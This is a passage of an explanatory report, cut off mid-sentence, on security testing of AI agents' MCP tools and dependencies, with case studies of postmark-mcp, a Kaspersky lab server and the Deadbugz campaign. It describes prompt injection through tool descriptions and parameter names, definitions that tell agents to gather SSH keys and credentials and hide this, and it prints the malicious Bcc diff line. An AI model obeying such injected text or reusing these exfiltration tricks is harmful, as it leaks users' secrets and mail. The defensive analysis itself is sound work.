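# Security testing of the tools and dependencies of AI agents beyond functional tests

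## The parts of an agent system and four ways to check them

An AI agent is a language model that a program runs in a loop. The model writes text, the program carries out any action the text requests, and the result goes back to the model as new text. The program carries out these actions through tools, which are functions for tasks such as sending an email or reading a file. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (Chu, 2026) defines an agent by its ability to perceive its environment, change it through such actions, keep state from one turn to the next and carry out plans.

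People who deploy agents often install tools written by others, and those tools depend on libraries from yet other authors. Any of this code can be malicious. Malicious code is hard to catch because it can steal data while doing its advertised job correctly, and so pass functional tests. Security testing therefore also includes inspecting the components and their origin, reading records of what the agent did, and monitoring the system while it runs.

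Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard from late 2024. In its July 2026 release post, the project reported close to half a billion monthly downloads of its main developer kits (Model Context Protocol, 2026). An MCP server is a program that offers tools to agents. The application that the user talks to, such as Claude Desktop, creates one client for each server it connects to (Model Context Protocol architecture guide). Servers can run locally on the user's machine or remotely on the operator's machines.

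### One request, step by step

Suppose a user types "email this invoice" into an assistant connected to an email server. The sequence below condenses a ten-step account from *MCP Tools*, by Beretta, Carlock and Pease, published by Elastic, which sells security products.

1. The client asks the server for its tools, and the server returns a tool definition for each: a name (`send_email`), a description of what the tool does, and a schema of the inputs it expects (recipient, subject, file). The server's author wrote all of this text.
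2. The client sends the user's sentence to the model together with the definitions. This is the application maker's code, running with the user's permissions.
3. The model picks `send_email` and writes the arguments. It typically runs on its provider's computers and has no permissions on the user's machine. Its output is a request that the client can carry out or refuse.
4. Depending on its design, the client shows the call to the user and waits for approval.
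5. The client sends the call to the server, and the server author's code runs. A local server has the user's permissions. A remote one has its operator's, plus whatever access the user has granted it, such as a key to the mail account.
6. That code calls libraries, for instance to build the message and open an encrypted connection. The libraries' authors may be strangers to the server's author as well as to the user, yet their code runs inside the server with all of the server's permissions.
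7. The server returns a result such as "message sent". The client passes it to the model, and the model writes an answer for the user.

Code therefore runs with the same permissions even when the user has never heard of its author. According to a vendor's glossary entry, PolicyLayer's *What is a Local MCP Server?*, a local server runs as an ordinary process under the user's account and can read the same files and use the same cloud credentials as the user. An email tool needs very little of that access. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* recommends, but does not require, that clients start local servers in a sandbox with restricted access to files and the network. A client that offers one-click installation must show the user the exact command that will run, but the command names a package without showing its contents.

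Approval at step 4 offers less protection than it appears to. The Model Context Protocol specification describes tools as arbitrary code execution and calls for explicit consent before any tool is used, but it notes that the protocol cannot enforce this. Beretta and colleagues observe that users of agents now accept tool calls wholesale. Even a user who reads every request sees only the arguments, which can be identical for a safe tool and a malicious one.

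The definitions at step 1 can themselves carry an attack, because the model reads them as part of its input and may follow instructions in them. Beretta and colleagues construct an example in which a tool called `daily_quote`, which returns an inspirational quote, has a description that tells the model to add a hidden 0.5% fee whenever it uses a separate payment tool. This can work even if the model never calls `daily_quote`. A parameter name alone can also leak data. If a field is called `summary_of_environment_details`, the model may fill in file contents or chat history unasked, and the client then sends them to the server as ordinary arguments.

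For the call itself, Yang, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *SoK*, a survey of attacks on agents' tools and data, offer a compact notation:

Invoke(T, θ, C) → (o, Δ)

Here T is the tool, θ is the arguments, and C is the context in which it runs, including credentials and accessible files. The call produces an output o and a set of side effects Δ. For the invoice, o is "message sent" and Δ should contain only the sent email. If the code also read a password file and sent it somewhere, Δ would include those actions too, but the output shown to the model and the user would still be "message sent".

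### Skills, registries and what lies beneath a tool

Agents also load skills, which are packages of written instructions for a kind of task. In the open format Agent Skills, a skill is a folder with a `SKILL.md` file that contains a name, a description and the instructions. The folder can also include scripts and reference material. A skill can cause harm through a script that runs or through written instructions that the model follows, and a scanner that reads only code misses harmful instructions.

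People install skills and packages from public registries, such as npm for JavaScript, PyPI for Python and ClawHub for skills. ClawHub's *Agent Skills* listing gives a single command for installation. Registries differ in what they verify, and may verify little. The official Model Context Protocol (MCP) Registry ties a server's name to a verified GitHub account or web domain, so users can tell who published it, but its documentation leaves security scanning to the underlying package registries and downstream marketplaces. The registry does remove malware, but its *Moderation Policy* tells users to assume minimal or no moderation.

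A dependency is a third-party library that a program needs. A library that the email server's author chose for building messages is a direct dependency. If that library needs another one to handle character encodings, the second is a transitive dependency of the server, and the author may never have heard of it. The chain can run several levels deep, and each level has its own maintainers, any of whom can publish a bad release or have their password stolen by someone who does. Common package managers let a package execute code during installation, as Yang and colleagues point out, so a malicious transitive dependency can do harm before the agent first uses the tool. The risk is greater when agents install packages themselves during a task, since they treat the installation as one more step towards the goal.

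### How an update reaches a running agent

Checking a component once is of little use if it can change the next day. For many local servers, the configuration holds a command that fetches the package and runs it at launch without permanently installing it, as PolicyLayer describes. If the command doesn't specify a version, a restart can bring in a release that nobody on the user's side has inspected. The operator of a remote server can replace the code on its own machines without changing any file on the user's side.

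Tool definitions can change too. In the July 2026 version of the standard, a client subscribes to change notices, the server sends one when its tools change, and the client requests the list again, according to the tools specification of the Model Context Protocol (2026). The standard only recommends that servers send the notice. Clients receive it only if they have subscribed, and they may keep using a stored copy of the old list for a period that the server suggests. A user's bug report on the forum of the code editor Cursor, *MCP*, describes Cursor and Claude Code ignoring the notice altogether under the previous version of the standard. An updated definition can therefore reach different users at different times, and Beretta and colleagues warn that a change after approval does not necessarily trigger a new request for approval. The notice also covers only the list of tools. If an author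 rewrites the function behind `send_email` without changing its definition, the protocol has no way to signal the change.

Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) records that, in the new version, the tool list may no longer vary between connections. This helps auditors because they should receive the same list as any user with the same access rights, although a malicious server can break the rule.

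The usual defence against silent change is pinning, which means fixing a component to one exact version or to a hash, a short fingerprint computed from its contents that changes whenever they do. Publishers of packages in the MCPB format must supply a hash with their listing. The registry does not check it, but clients do before they install, according to Model Context Protocol's *Package Types*. Pinning only keeps a component the same, so a package that was malicious when it was pinned stays malicious. For a remote server, the user has no code to pin, only the tool definitions.

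### Compromised and vulnerable components

A compromised component is a tool, skill or library that someone has deliberately made malicious. A vulnerable component has an unintended flaw that an attacker could exploit. Beretta and colleagues give the example of a tool that takes a string and passes it to the operating system as a command, so anyone who can influence the string can run commands on that machine. Such a flaw does nothing until someone exploits it, whereas ordinary use is enough to trigger a compromised component.

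Flaws and tampering call for different searches. Once someone has found and reported a flaw, a public advisory lists the affected versions, and software can match that list against what is installed. Red Hat's *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* recommends this matching, known as software composition analysis, for the libraries that MCP servers use. Against tampering, it recommends verifying the integrity of every dependency and scanning for malware. A newly compromised release has no advisory because nobody has noticed the problem yet, so a scanner has to judge the code or its behaviour directly. This is difficult when the suspicious act, such as opening a network connection, is also the component's job.

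Updating dependencies quickly fixes known flaws, but it also spreads compromised releases. Pinning dependencies to fixed versions slows that spread and keeps old flaws in place, so a team that pins has to keep reading security advisories and change its pinned versions deliberately.

### Four checks

A functional test gives a component an input the developer chose and compares the result with the expected one, normally before release. A test of `send_email` might send a message to a dummy address and confirm that it arrives with its attachment. In the notation above, the test covers o and the part of Δ that the developer thought to check. The test can pass despite unwanted extras in Δ unless someone wrote a check for them, and it does not run code that the chosen inputs never reach.

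A dependency audit is an inspection of what is installed, where it came from, and what known or visible problems it has. Auditors can match versions to advisories, compare hashes, and examine provenance attestations, which are signed statements of which source code and build process produced a package. They can also read the code, or the text of skills and tool definitions, for signs of malice. Beretta and colleagues show a rudimentary version of this last check, in which a language model marks each tool definition as malicious or harmless and gives a reason. They present it as a demonstration, not a production method. Teams run audits at installation or on a schedule.

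An action log is a stored record of what the agent and its tools did, for someone to read afterwards. The Model Context Protocol specification also recommends, but does not require, that clients log tool use for audit. A client can record the call it sent and the result it received, which are steps 5 and 7 of the invoice example. Only the server or the operating system could record what the libraries did at step 6, because that activity never passes through the client.

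Continuous monitoring automatically evaluates a system's behaviour while it runs and can raise an alarm or block an action. A monitor can run on the network, in the operating system, or at a gateway between clients and servers. Since the July 2026 version of the Model Context Protocol (MCP), requests to servers over the web carry the tool's name in a header, so a gateway can permit or refuse a call without parsing the message body, according to the protocol's release post. A gateway between client and server can't monitor connections that the server itself opens to third parties, but network monitoring on the server's machine can cover those.

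Only some forms of auditing and monitoring can prevent harm. An audit can do so if it runs before installation and can block the package, whereas a weekly audit may find a package that has already been in use for days. A monitor can prevent harm if it blocks the action before it happens. One that only raises an alarm may do so after the data have left, though the alarm can still limit the damage. Action logs record only what has already happened. Functional tests run early enough to prevent harm, but a compromised component that still does its job will pass them.

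Which check could have worked in a given case depends on where the malicious behaviour sits and when it runs. It may sit in a tool definition or skill text, in the component's own code, or in a dependency beneath it. It may run at installation, at start-up, as soon as the model reads a description, at each call, or only under some trigger. Once both are known, one can work out what each of the four checks revealed and what it could have revealed, which are often different. For example, if a tool leaked data while nobody was monitoring the network, the incident alone does not show whether monitoring would have caught the leak. That depends on whether the leak would have stood out from the tool's normal traffic.

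## How much of a library a test suite exercises

A developer who updates a library usually runs the project's tests and keeps the new version if they pass. Services such as Dependabot automate this by proposing each new release and showing whether the tests still pass. Hejderup and Gousios (2022), in *Can we trust tests to automate dependency updates?*, measured how far developers can trust that result. They studied ordinary bugs in Java libraries, not attacks on agents, but one of their motivating examples is an attack in which a malicious maintainer hid code for stealing bitcoin wallets in the npm package event-stream and its users did not notice.

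### The Java experiment

Hejderup and Gousios sampled 1,823 Java projects from GitHub that displayed at least one quality badge, such as one from a service that reports test coverage. They took a badge as a sign that the project had tests. Of these projects, 818 compiled and contained tests, 521 worked with the software that records calls, and 262 with the software that plants faults.

To count calls, the researchers first analysed each project's code without running it and listed every library function it could reach, directly or through other libraries. They then ran the tests and recorded which of those functions ran. Dependency coverage is the ratio of the two:

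coverage = library functions that ran during the tests / library functions the project can reach

The median project's tests covered 58% of its calls to direct dependencies. Including paths to transitive dependencies lowered the median to 21%. In 67 projects, the tests covered less than 10% of the direct calls. These figures are somewhat too low because the list of reachable functions includes some that are never called in practice.

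The 1,122,420 planted faults were small edits to library code, such as replacing a minus sign with a plus or "greater than" with "greater than or equal". Each edit simulated one faulty update. A project's tests caught a fault if at least one test failed.

| | Direct dependencies | Transitive dependencies |
|---|---|---|
| Calls that the tests covered (median, 521 projects) | 58% | 21% |
| Planted faults that the tests caught (mean, 262 projects) | 47% | 35% |
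| Planted faults that static analysis flagged (mean, 262 projects) | 74% | 64% |

The researchers planted faults only in library functions that the tests already ran. Tests that missed a fault therefore ran the function but either skipped the altered line or checked nothing it affected. Tests are less likely to catch a fault placed anywhere in the library code that a project uses. Multiplying mean coverage (55% for direct dependencies, 26% for transitive ones) by the mean catch rate suggests that they would catch roughly a quarter of such faults in direct dependencies and a tenth in transitive ones. This estimate is crude because the coverage and catch rates come from different sets of projects.

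Hejderup and Gousios built Uppdatera, the static analysis tool in the last row. It compares a library's old and new source code to find the functions that changed, and flags the update if the project can reach any of them. Its misses came mostly from libraries that choose or generate code at run time, because source analysis can't follow those calls. On 22 real updates, Uppdatera flagged all four that the researchers judged unsafe, while the tests passed three of them. But Uppdatera also raises more false alarms than tests do. It flagged 7 of the 15 safe updates, often because it could not tell a harmless rewrite from a change in behaviour.

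That oversensitivity is partly an advantage for security. Uppdatera could flag an added line that copies data elsewhere, even if the function's result stays the same, because the line changes the code. A person would still have to read the change and recognise it as theft. The method also needs an earlier, clean version for comparison, and it can miss code that runs at installation, outside any function the project calls.

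### Later evidence, and agents

The experiment appears not to have been replicated, but Monce, Degueule and colleagues (2025) tried a much blunter kind of fault in *Client–Library Compatibility Testing with API Interaction Snapshots*. In two Java libraries used by 27 projects, they replaced the whole body of one library function at a time with a default result such as zero. The projects' tests detected 141 of 158 replacements (89%), again counting only functions that the tests reached. Compared with the 47% for small edits, this suggests that tests are good at detecting when a library function stops working and much worse at detecting when it works slightly differently.

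Nobody seems to have measured the same thing for the third-party tools that agents call. *Complex Agents, Shallow Tests* (Xiong, Ge and colleagues, 2026) comes closest. It examines the agents' own code, meaning the program around the model, in ten widely used open-source agents, including OpenClaw and OpenHands. The tests ran 49% of that code's lines on average. In the part that handles the model's output, they caught 34% of planted faults, ranging from 4% for RD-Agent to 71% for Kimi Code. About 38% of the faults were in code that no test ran, and another 26% ran without making any test fail. Developers who test their own code this thinly probably don't test other people's tools more thoroughly, though the study offers no direct evidence on that.

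### Why an attacker would do better than a planted fault

Even the 47% and 35% probably overstate how often tests would catch an attacker. The sample favoured projects with visible quality badges, and the faults were only in code that tests already reached. More importantly, a planted fault typically changes a value that the library returns to the project, where an assertion may catch it. An attacker who wants to stay hidden leaves a tool call's output o unchanged and adds something to its side effects Δ instead.

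Monce and colleagues ran the tests and also recorded every value that passed between project and library, then compared the recordings from before and after each change. This caught 151 of the 158 replacements. Some of the seven it missed changed only what the library read or wrote elsewhere, not what it returned, so they didn't show up in the recordings.

A test suite can catch malicious code when the attacker has made a mistake, such as writing code that crashes, slows the program down or fails when the test machine has no network. But running the tests also runs the malicious code, with access to any passwords and keys on the test machine, so the code may have stolen them before the results appear.

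### Four reasons why functional tests miss a compromise

A test checks only what its author thought to assert. One project in the study by Monce and colleagues converts web tables into spreadsheets, and its test confirms that the conversion finishes without an error. When the researchers disabled a function in the underlying library, the spreadsheet lost rows and columns, but the test still passed. Developers who don't check the shape of the spreadsheet, which the program exists to produce, are unlikely to have checked that no third party receives a copy. An attacker who writes a tool also writes the tests that come with it.

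Common coverage measures can hide how much code the tests never run. *AgentAssay* (2026), a proposal for testing agents, defines tool coverage as the share of an agent's tools that the tests call at least once. A tool called once with a trivial input counts as much as one called with many different inputs. *AgentAssay* acknowledges this limitation and tries to address it with a separate measure. An agent can therefore have 100% tool coverage even if the tests never run most of the code behind its tools.

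Tests also often replace the component that needs checking with a mock, a stand-in that returns a prepared answer. Mocks make tests fast and repeatable, but the tests never run the code that the mocks replace, so they can't detect whether that code has been compromised. For example, the example test for a search tool in *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026) replaces the search service with a mock that returns one invented result, then checks that the tool passes it on. Xiong and colleagues found extensive use of mocks in all ten agents, and mocking may be increasing as agents write more of the tests. *Are Coding Agents Generating Over-Mocked Tests?* (Hora and Robbes, 2026) found that 36% of coding agents' commits to test files added mocks, compared with 26% of other commits. Mocks may also behave differently from the components they replace. *Executable but Unfaithful* (Ning, Dong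 and Yang, 2026) found deviations in model-written mocks that can go unnoticed when tests pass.

A test that uses a mock doesn't exercise the code the mock replaces, but it can still check how the tool calls that code. The test in the *Guide* also asserts that the tool called the search service exactly once, with the expected arguments. The same assertion in a test of an email tool would fail if the tool's own code added an extra recipient.

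Finally, the tested version may not be the version that runs. Hejderup and Gousios describe how developers declare a range of acceptable versions, so "1.0.0 or later" automatically admits every future release. *How are AI agents used?* (2026), a study of 177,000 MCP tools, gives a typical installation command that requests the latest version of a browser tool, so a test of one person's copy may not cover the next person's. The mismatch can be greater for remote servers because, according to *Exposed by Design* (2026), servers in production may differ substantially from their registry descriptions. Pinning exact versions prevents the mismatch for local packages only if it covers transitive dependencies too.

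### The arithmetic of hidden triggers

More testing seems the obvious remedy, and for behaviour that appears at random one can calculate how much it helps. Suppose a tool misbehaves with probability p on each call, and that a test would notice if it did. One test misses the behaviour with probability 1 − p, so n independent tests all miss it with probability

(1 − p)ⁿ

After n clean runs, the values of p that remain plausible at 95% confidence are those for which this probability is at least 5%. Setting (1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05 gives

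p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n)

which is close to 3/n when n is large. For n = 300 the result is just under 1%. Three hundred clean runs are thus compatible with a tool that misbehaves on one call in a hundred, and if an agent calls that tool a thousand times a day, this means about ten incidents a day. Getting the bound down to one call in a thousand takes about 3,000 clean runs, and one in a million takes about three million.

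The calculation assumes that p is the same in tests and in real use. That is reasonable for an accidental fault that depends on timing or unusual data, but an attacker who chooses the trigger can make p zero in testing and one in use. The code might check the date, look for the environment settings that mark an automated test machine, or wait until it finds a real cloud password. It might also change its behaviour only on the third call, which would let it pass any number of tests that each start the tool afresh and call it once. In all these cases, clean test runs provide no evidence about p in real use, whether there are 300 of them or three million.

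A backdoor is even harder to trigger when doing so requires a secret key. An attacker planted a backdoor in the compression library xz that activates only on input signed with a particular private key. Without that key, even a tester who knows exactly where the backdoor is cannot trigger it unless they break the cryptography. *ROSA* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and colleagues, 2025) excludes xz from its benchmark of backdoors for this reason.

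### Fuzzing and property-based testing

Developers needn't choose test inputs by hand. A fuzzer generates them automatically, often millions of them. The common kind makes small random changes to earlier inputs and keeps those that reach new code, so it can reach parts of a program that no hand-written test runs. In property-based testing, the developer states a rule that should hold for every input, such as that decompressing a compressed file returns the original, and a tool searches for an input that breaks the rule.

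Both methods widen coverage, and modern fuzzers can guess simple secret words in a program's code. But more inputs reveal a problem only if the test can recognise a failure. Fuzzers usually look for crashes, and Kokkonis and colleagues point out that a well-written backdoor does not crash. *MCPGuard* (2026) describes programs such as Schemathesis, which derive both inputs and checks from an interface's schema. An email tool that returns "message sent" in the right format satisfies its schema, whatever else it did. Security testers often search for specific types of flaw. *VIPER-MCP* (2026), for example, looks for flaws in MCP servers, such as command injection, that let outside input reach a dangerous operation. A tool designed to steal data may contain no such flaw.

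Kokkonis and colleagues built ROSA, a tool that looks for backdoors without needing to know what they do. It relies on the rule that similar inputs should cause similar requests to the operating system, known as system calls. ROSA first fuzzes a program for one minute to collect ordinary inputs. It then fuzzes for hours, matches each new input with the ordinary one that ran the most similar code, and reports any pair whose types of system call differ. For example, it would report a wrong password that starts a new process when a similar one only produces an error message. The team tested ROSA on seven real backdoors and ten planted by a researcher. It found each at least once, though one only after the team supplied more specific starting inputs. It succeeded in 156 of 180 eight-hour runs and left a person an average of seven suspicious inputs to examine. In the 24 failed runs, the fuzzer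 never triggered the backdoor.

ROSA compares a program with itself, so it needs some clean behaviour as a baseline. This suits code that misbehaves only after a hidden trigger. A component that leaks on every call provides no such baseline.

For such a component, someone has to state what the tool may not do. *A Formal Security Framework for MCP-Based AI Agents* (2026) gives examples of suitable properties, such as requiring a tool's definition at each call to be identical to the one the user approved. A client can check this by comparing hashes, though the code behind the definition can still change. Another property is that information must never flow from a higher security level to a lower one across a trust boundary. This would rule out most data theft, but testing it requires labelling the data and monitoring every route by which it can leave.

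A narrower property is often easier to test. For an email tool, one such property could be that each message goes only to the recipients in the request. The tester would run the tool against a dummy mail service that records everything it receives. A tool that copied every message to an outsider, as postmark-mcp did, would fail on the first call, without any fuzzing. The test would miss a tool that sent the copy over a separate connection, unless the tester also recorded the tool's other network traffic.

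## The postmark-mcp email tool, which copied every message to an outsider

Postmark is a service that other companies' software uses to send email, such as receipts and password resets. In 2025 it released an experimental MCP server on GitHub that lets an AI assistant send email from the user's Postmark account. It did not publish the server on npm, so the name `postmark-mcp` was free there. On 15 September 2025, the npm user phanpak uploaded a copy of Postmark's code under that name.

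The copy worked, and Koi Security, which sells software for screening packages and MCP servers, counts 15 good versions before version 1.0.16. That version came out on 17 September, according to The Hacker News (2025). It added one line to the function that sends an email, putting an address at the domain giftshop.club in the blind-copy (Bcc) field. An outsider therefore received the whole message, including attachments, and the other recipients couldn't see the extra address.

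Koi reports that its scanning software flagged the new version. The developer did not reply when Koi's researchers made contact, but deleted the package from npm. Copies that were already installed kept sending emails to the outsider until users removed them. Koi described the package as the first malicious MCP server found in real use. Infosecurity Magazine's *Malicious AI Agent Server Reportedly Steals Emails* dates Koi's report to 25 September. Postmark said it had nothing to do with the package and that its own service was unaffected.

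The malicious version copied ordinary emails but not those built from a template, although some descriptions of the incident say it copied every email. Snyk's *Malicious MCP Server on npm postmark-mcp Harvests Emails* (2025), from another security vendor, reproduces the full code of version 1.0.18, the last release. The code handles the two kinds of email in separate functions, and only the one for ordinary emails contains the Bcc line. Koi also warns that a tool can be legitimate "for months" before it turns malicious, but this one was clean for only two days, so users had almost no track record to go on. They probably trusted the tool's name. They may also have trusted the author field in the code, which still named the Postmark developer who wrote the original, although anyone can type any name into that field.

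The number of victims is unknown. The Hacker News gives a total of 1,643 downloads, but downloads are not users, since a build server that reinstalls its packages every night adds one each time. Koi's figures of 300 organisations and 3,000 to 15,000 stolen emails a day are its own estimates, from this calculation:

1,500 downloads a week × 20% in use = 300 organisations

300 organisations × 10 to 50 emails a day = 3,000 to 15,000 emails a day

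Koi calls this a "guestimate". It gives no basis for the 20% or for the 10 to 50 emails, and it treats each download still in use as a separate organisation. Postmark could presumably count the stolen emails, since they all passed through its systems, but its public statement gives no number.

### Two tests of the same tool

Suppose a developer wants to check the `sendEmail` tool before accepting an update. Here are two possible tests in pseudocode:

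```
args = {to: "ana@test.example", subject: "Invoice", textBody: "Due Friday"}

test "the tool reports success":
    reply = call_tool("sendEmail", args)
    assert reply contains "Email sent successfully"

test "the message goes to Ana and nobody else":
    fake = start_fake_postmark()    # records requests, delivers nothing
    call_tool("sendEmail", args)
    message = fake.recorded_message()
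    assert message.To + message.Cc + message.Bcc == ["ana@test.example"]
```

The results follow from the code that Snyk published:

| | Version 1.0.15 (clean) | Version 1.0.18 (malicious) |
|---|---|---|
| Reply to the agent | "Email sent successfully" | "Email sent successfully" |
| First test | passes | passes |
| Recipients in the recorded message | Ana | Ana and the giftshop.club address |
| Second test | passes | fails |

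The server builds its reply from the recipient and subject that the agent supplied, plus a message ID from Postmark, so the reply looks the same whoever else receives the email. Postmark's own response may not reveal the extra recipient either, since the example in *Send a single email* includes the To address and no Bcc. Postmark also offers a test key that lets developers check that their data are valid without delivering any messages, but a message with an extra Bcc is valid. A developer who sends a real email and opens it in Ana's inbox will see nothing wrong either, because blind copies are hidden from the other recipients.

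The second test works only if it compares the whole list of recipients. An assertion that Ana is among them passes on both versions. The added line was in the server's own code, so a test could replace Postmark's client library with a mock and still record the Bcc. That would not work if an attacker had changed the library itself. A fake of Postmark's web service covers both cases because it receives the message after all of the tool's code has run.

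Few suites are likely to contain the second test. The malicious package came with no test command, only commands to start and inspect the server. People who install a ready-made tool rarely write tests for it, and those who do would naturally work from its definition. The definition of `sendEmail` lists eight inputs but no Bcc, so a tester would have no reason to think of that field. The second test also takes more work to set up. This server contacts Postmark at start-up to verify its key, so the fake has to answer that request before it can receive any email.

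Even a careful maintainer may not test who receives each email. Postmark describes a suite of 52 tests for a later version of its official server. They cover logging, the validation of notification settings and the server's configuration. Separate checks send real emails from a live account. Postmark doesn't mention a test that compares recipient lists, though the suite may contain one.

The second test covers only one effect of one function. The template function would need its own test. The second test would also miss a changed reply-to address, which would direct customers' answers to an outsider. More seriously, it would miss theft of the key to the user's Postmark account, which the server needs to send email. According to Postmark's *Messages API*, anyone with that key can retrieve the text of sent messages, which Postmark keeps for 45 days by default. A malicious server could send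 the key to its author once and never alter an email, so the recipient list would be correct in every test.

### Comparing the versions line by line

The extra line is easy to find by comparing the two releases. An auditor downloads both packages, unpacks them and has a program list every line that differs, which npm can do with a single command, `npm diff`. Between 1.0.15 and 1.0.18, Snyk found one notable change, which looks roughly like this:

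```
  To: to,
+ Bcc: '...@giftshop.club',
```

An auditor doesn't need to know much about malware to ask why an email tool has a fixed recipient. The line was easy to spot here because the server was a single file of readable JavaScript. It would have been much harder to find among thousands of changed lines or in code compressed by a build tool. Comparing the package with its earlier version also misses changes in its dependencies, and `postmark-mcp` accepted a range of versions for each of its five libraries.

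Someone who first installed the package after 17 September had no trusted earlier copy to compare it with. They could have compared it with Postmark's GitHub repository instead, since The Hacker News describes the package as a replica of the original apart from the one line. Checking whether Postmark had published the package would have been simpler, because Postmark had never published an MCP server on npm. The official server is now on npm as `@activecampaign/postmark-mcp`, under the name of Postmark's parent company.

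Auditors would have had to work fast, since the developer released as many as 19 versions in three days. A configuration that always fetches the latest version would have run each one without review. Pinning to version 1.0.15 would have kept the Bcc line out until the user chose to update. Some teams instead wait a fixed time before adopting any release, hoping others will find the problems first. A seven-day wait would have ended on 24 September, the day before Koi published its report.

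Koi's software automated the same idea by flagging a change in behaviour between releases. Koi says it did this as soon as version 1.0.16 introduced the Bcc. Koi does not explain how the software detected the change or how often it flags harmless updates, so the software's reliability is hard to judge from this one success.

### Scanning for known problems

A scan for known advisories would have found nothing for about nine days after the malicious release. OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), an entry in a public database of vulnerable and malicious packages, appeared early on 26 September. Snyk's *Malicious Package Affecting postmark-mcp package* (2025) followed the same day and lists no CVE number, the standard identifier for a publicly known flaw. A scanner that relied only on CVE numbers would presumably have missed the package even then.

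The advisories were still useful for finding installed copies. Snyk says its dependency scanner detects `postmark-mcp` when a project uses it as a dependency, but such a scan may not cover servers that an AI application starts from its configuration file.

Snyk also recommends its MCP-Scan, which searches MCP servers for problems such as malicious instructions in tool definitions. Snyk acknowledges that this attack was in the code, not in text meant for the model. The definition of `sendEmail` was harmless even in the malicious version, so a scanner that checked only definitions would not have detected the attack.

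### Where the extra recipient appeared

The agent's own log could hold the recipient, subject and text that the model supplied, along with the reply. It did not contain the Bcc, because the server added that after receiving the call. The malicious server's log held the recipient, subject and message ID but not the Bcc, because the server's author decided what to log. Release 1.0.18 also reported its version to clients as 1.0.0, so a log of reported server versions would not have revealed the update.

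Postmark's records did contain the evidence. Its Messages API returns the To, Cc and Bcc addresses of each message, together with a complete list of recipients. A user could combine these records with the agent's log in three steps:

1. Take the message ID from the tool's reply in the agent's log.
2. Ask Postmark for the message with that ID.
3. Compare its recipients with the address that the agent supplied.

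Any additional address is one that the agent did not request. Once Koi had published the attacker's address, affected users could search for it, and Koi, Snyk and Postmark all advised people to check their email logs. Postmark retains messages for 45 days by default, so the first copied ones would disappear around 1 November. Customers can shorten this period to seven days, in which case the earliest evidence was gone by 24 September, before the public knew what to look for.

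A monitor could make the same comparison continuously. According to Postmark's *Delivery webhook*, Postmark can notify a customer's software for each recipient as soon as the receiving mail server accepts the message. An alarm based on these notices could have gone off at the first copied email. To prevent even that first leak, a company would need a checkpoint between the MCP server and Postmark that reads each request and rejects any recipient that wasn't in the agent's call. Both the alarm and the checkpoint would need exceptions, since companies may deliberately blind-copy their mail to an archive or a sales system. None of the accounts mentions a user who had either one.

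Monitoring the network connections of the user's machine would probably have revealed nothing. The malicious server sent its requests to Postmark, as the clean one did, and Postmark's systems delivered the copies, so the user's machine never had to contact giftshop.club. For the same reason, blocking outgoing traffic to that domain, as Snyk advised, would not have stopped the copying by itself. A sandbox that let the server connect only to Postmark would also have let every copy through.

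### Kaspersky's developer tool

Kaspersky, another security vendor, built a malicious MCP server to demonstrate a similar attack in a laboratory and described the experiment on its research site, Securelist. The server, `devtools-assistant`, was a Python package with three tools that analysed a project's structure, checked its configuration files and suggested improvements to the programming environment. All three worked as advertised in the code editor Cursor.

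Each tool also called a shared module disguised as a collector of project metrics. The module searched the project and other folders on the machine for passwords, cloud credentials, browser data, cryptocurrency wallets and SSH keys, which give access to other computers. It copied up to the first 100 KB of each file and sent the contents to an outside server in requests made to look like traffic to GitHub. It also passed a list of the files, with the secrets removed, to the three tools, which used the list to produce correct reports.

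The researchers then acted as an unsuspecting user. A network sensor flagged a request to an address that resembled GitHub's. They recorded the traffic, decoded it and found the test project's API key and database password. They read the source code only after a second program showed the server's process searching through files. Since the same team designed the attack and the laboratory, the experiment can't establish how often a sensor would catch a real attacker, who could also choose a less conspicuous destination.

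Logging every prompt and response, which Securelist recommends to catch hidden instructions and unexpected tool calls, would not have helped much in its own experiment, because the theft happened inside the server and the responses looked normal. Its advice to run servers in containers, with access only to the folders they need, would have helped more. A container limited to the project folder would have protected the SSH keys and browser passwords, though not the passwords stored in the project itself.

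A functional test with a broader assertion than the email test could also have caught this server. A tool that analyses local files has no need to contact other machines, so a tester could put a fake password in a dummy project, run each tool and assert that the server opens no outside connections. This would catch any theft over the network during the test, whatever the data or destination. Even a clean email tool would fail this test, because it has to contact an outside service to send anything.

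## Tools that changed after they were checked

The malicious `postmark-mcp` and Kaspersky's demonstration server both stole data on the first call, so a single test with the right assertion could have caught either. An attacker can avoid such a test by keeping the component harmless until the check is over. Security firms described three examples in the summer of 2026. In one, a server changed its tool definitions after a few calls. In another, a skill linked to a web page that its owner later rewrote. In the third, an attacker published clean copies of popular skills and added malicious instructions six days later.

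### Deadbugz, a server that counted calls

On 10 August 2026, one GitHub account opened 23 pull requests in 74 minutes. A pull request proposes a change to someone else's project, and the maintainers can merge or close it. Seventeen of these added a remote MCP server called `productivity-suite` to a project's configuration, so people who used the project with an agent might have connected to a server they never chose. Fogel (2026) described the campaign two days later in *Deadbugz*, written for Pillar Security, which sells security software for AI systems.

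The server offered two tools, `format_text` and `summarize`, and both worked. After a client had made three tool calls, the server returned altered definitions the next time that client requested the tool list. The tools kept their names, but their descriptions now contained instructions for the agent to look for SSH keys, cloud credentials and command history, and to hide this from the user. The server made the same kind of change to its prompts, which are ready-made messages that an MCP server can supply for a conversation.

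A remote server can't open files on the user's machine, so this attack would have worked only if the model followed the instructions and used the agent's other tools to read the files. Fogel documents the text that the server returned but doesn't report testing whether any model followed it.

The technique was more than a year old. Fogel recounts that in April 2025 the security firm Invariant Labs demonstrated a server with an innocuous tool whose description later changed. The new description manipulated the agent into sending the user's WhatsApp history to an attacker through a separate WhatsApp server that the user trusted. Testing the WhatsApp server would not have exposed the attack, because that server worked as it should.

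It isn't known whether Deadbugz had any victims. Fogel names none but doesn't say there were none. When Pillar reviewed the 23 pull requests, 19 were closed, four were open, and nobody had merged any through GitHub's merge mechanism. But a maintainer can copy a change by hand, which GitHub would not record as a merge. The operator may know more, since the server's code includes an option to send a notification when a client connects, makes its first call or reaches the threshold.

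### Why short tests saw only harmless definitions

Test suites often start a fresh copy of a server for each test, so that one test can't affect the next. The Deadbugz counter was held in memory, so each restart would reset it to zero. A suite of 40 tests with two calls each would make 80 calls without the counter ever passing two. A tester can't restart the remote version, but that server counted each client's calls separately, so connecting as a new client for each test would presumably have the same effect.

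Making more calls in one session isn't enough either, because the malicious text appeared only when the client asked for the definitions again:

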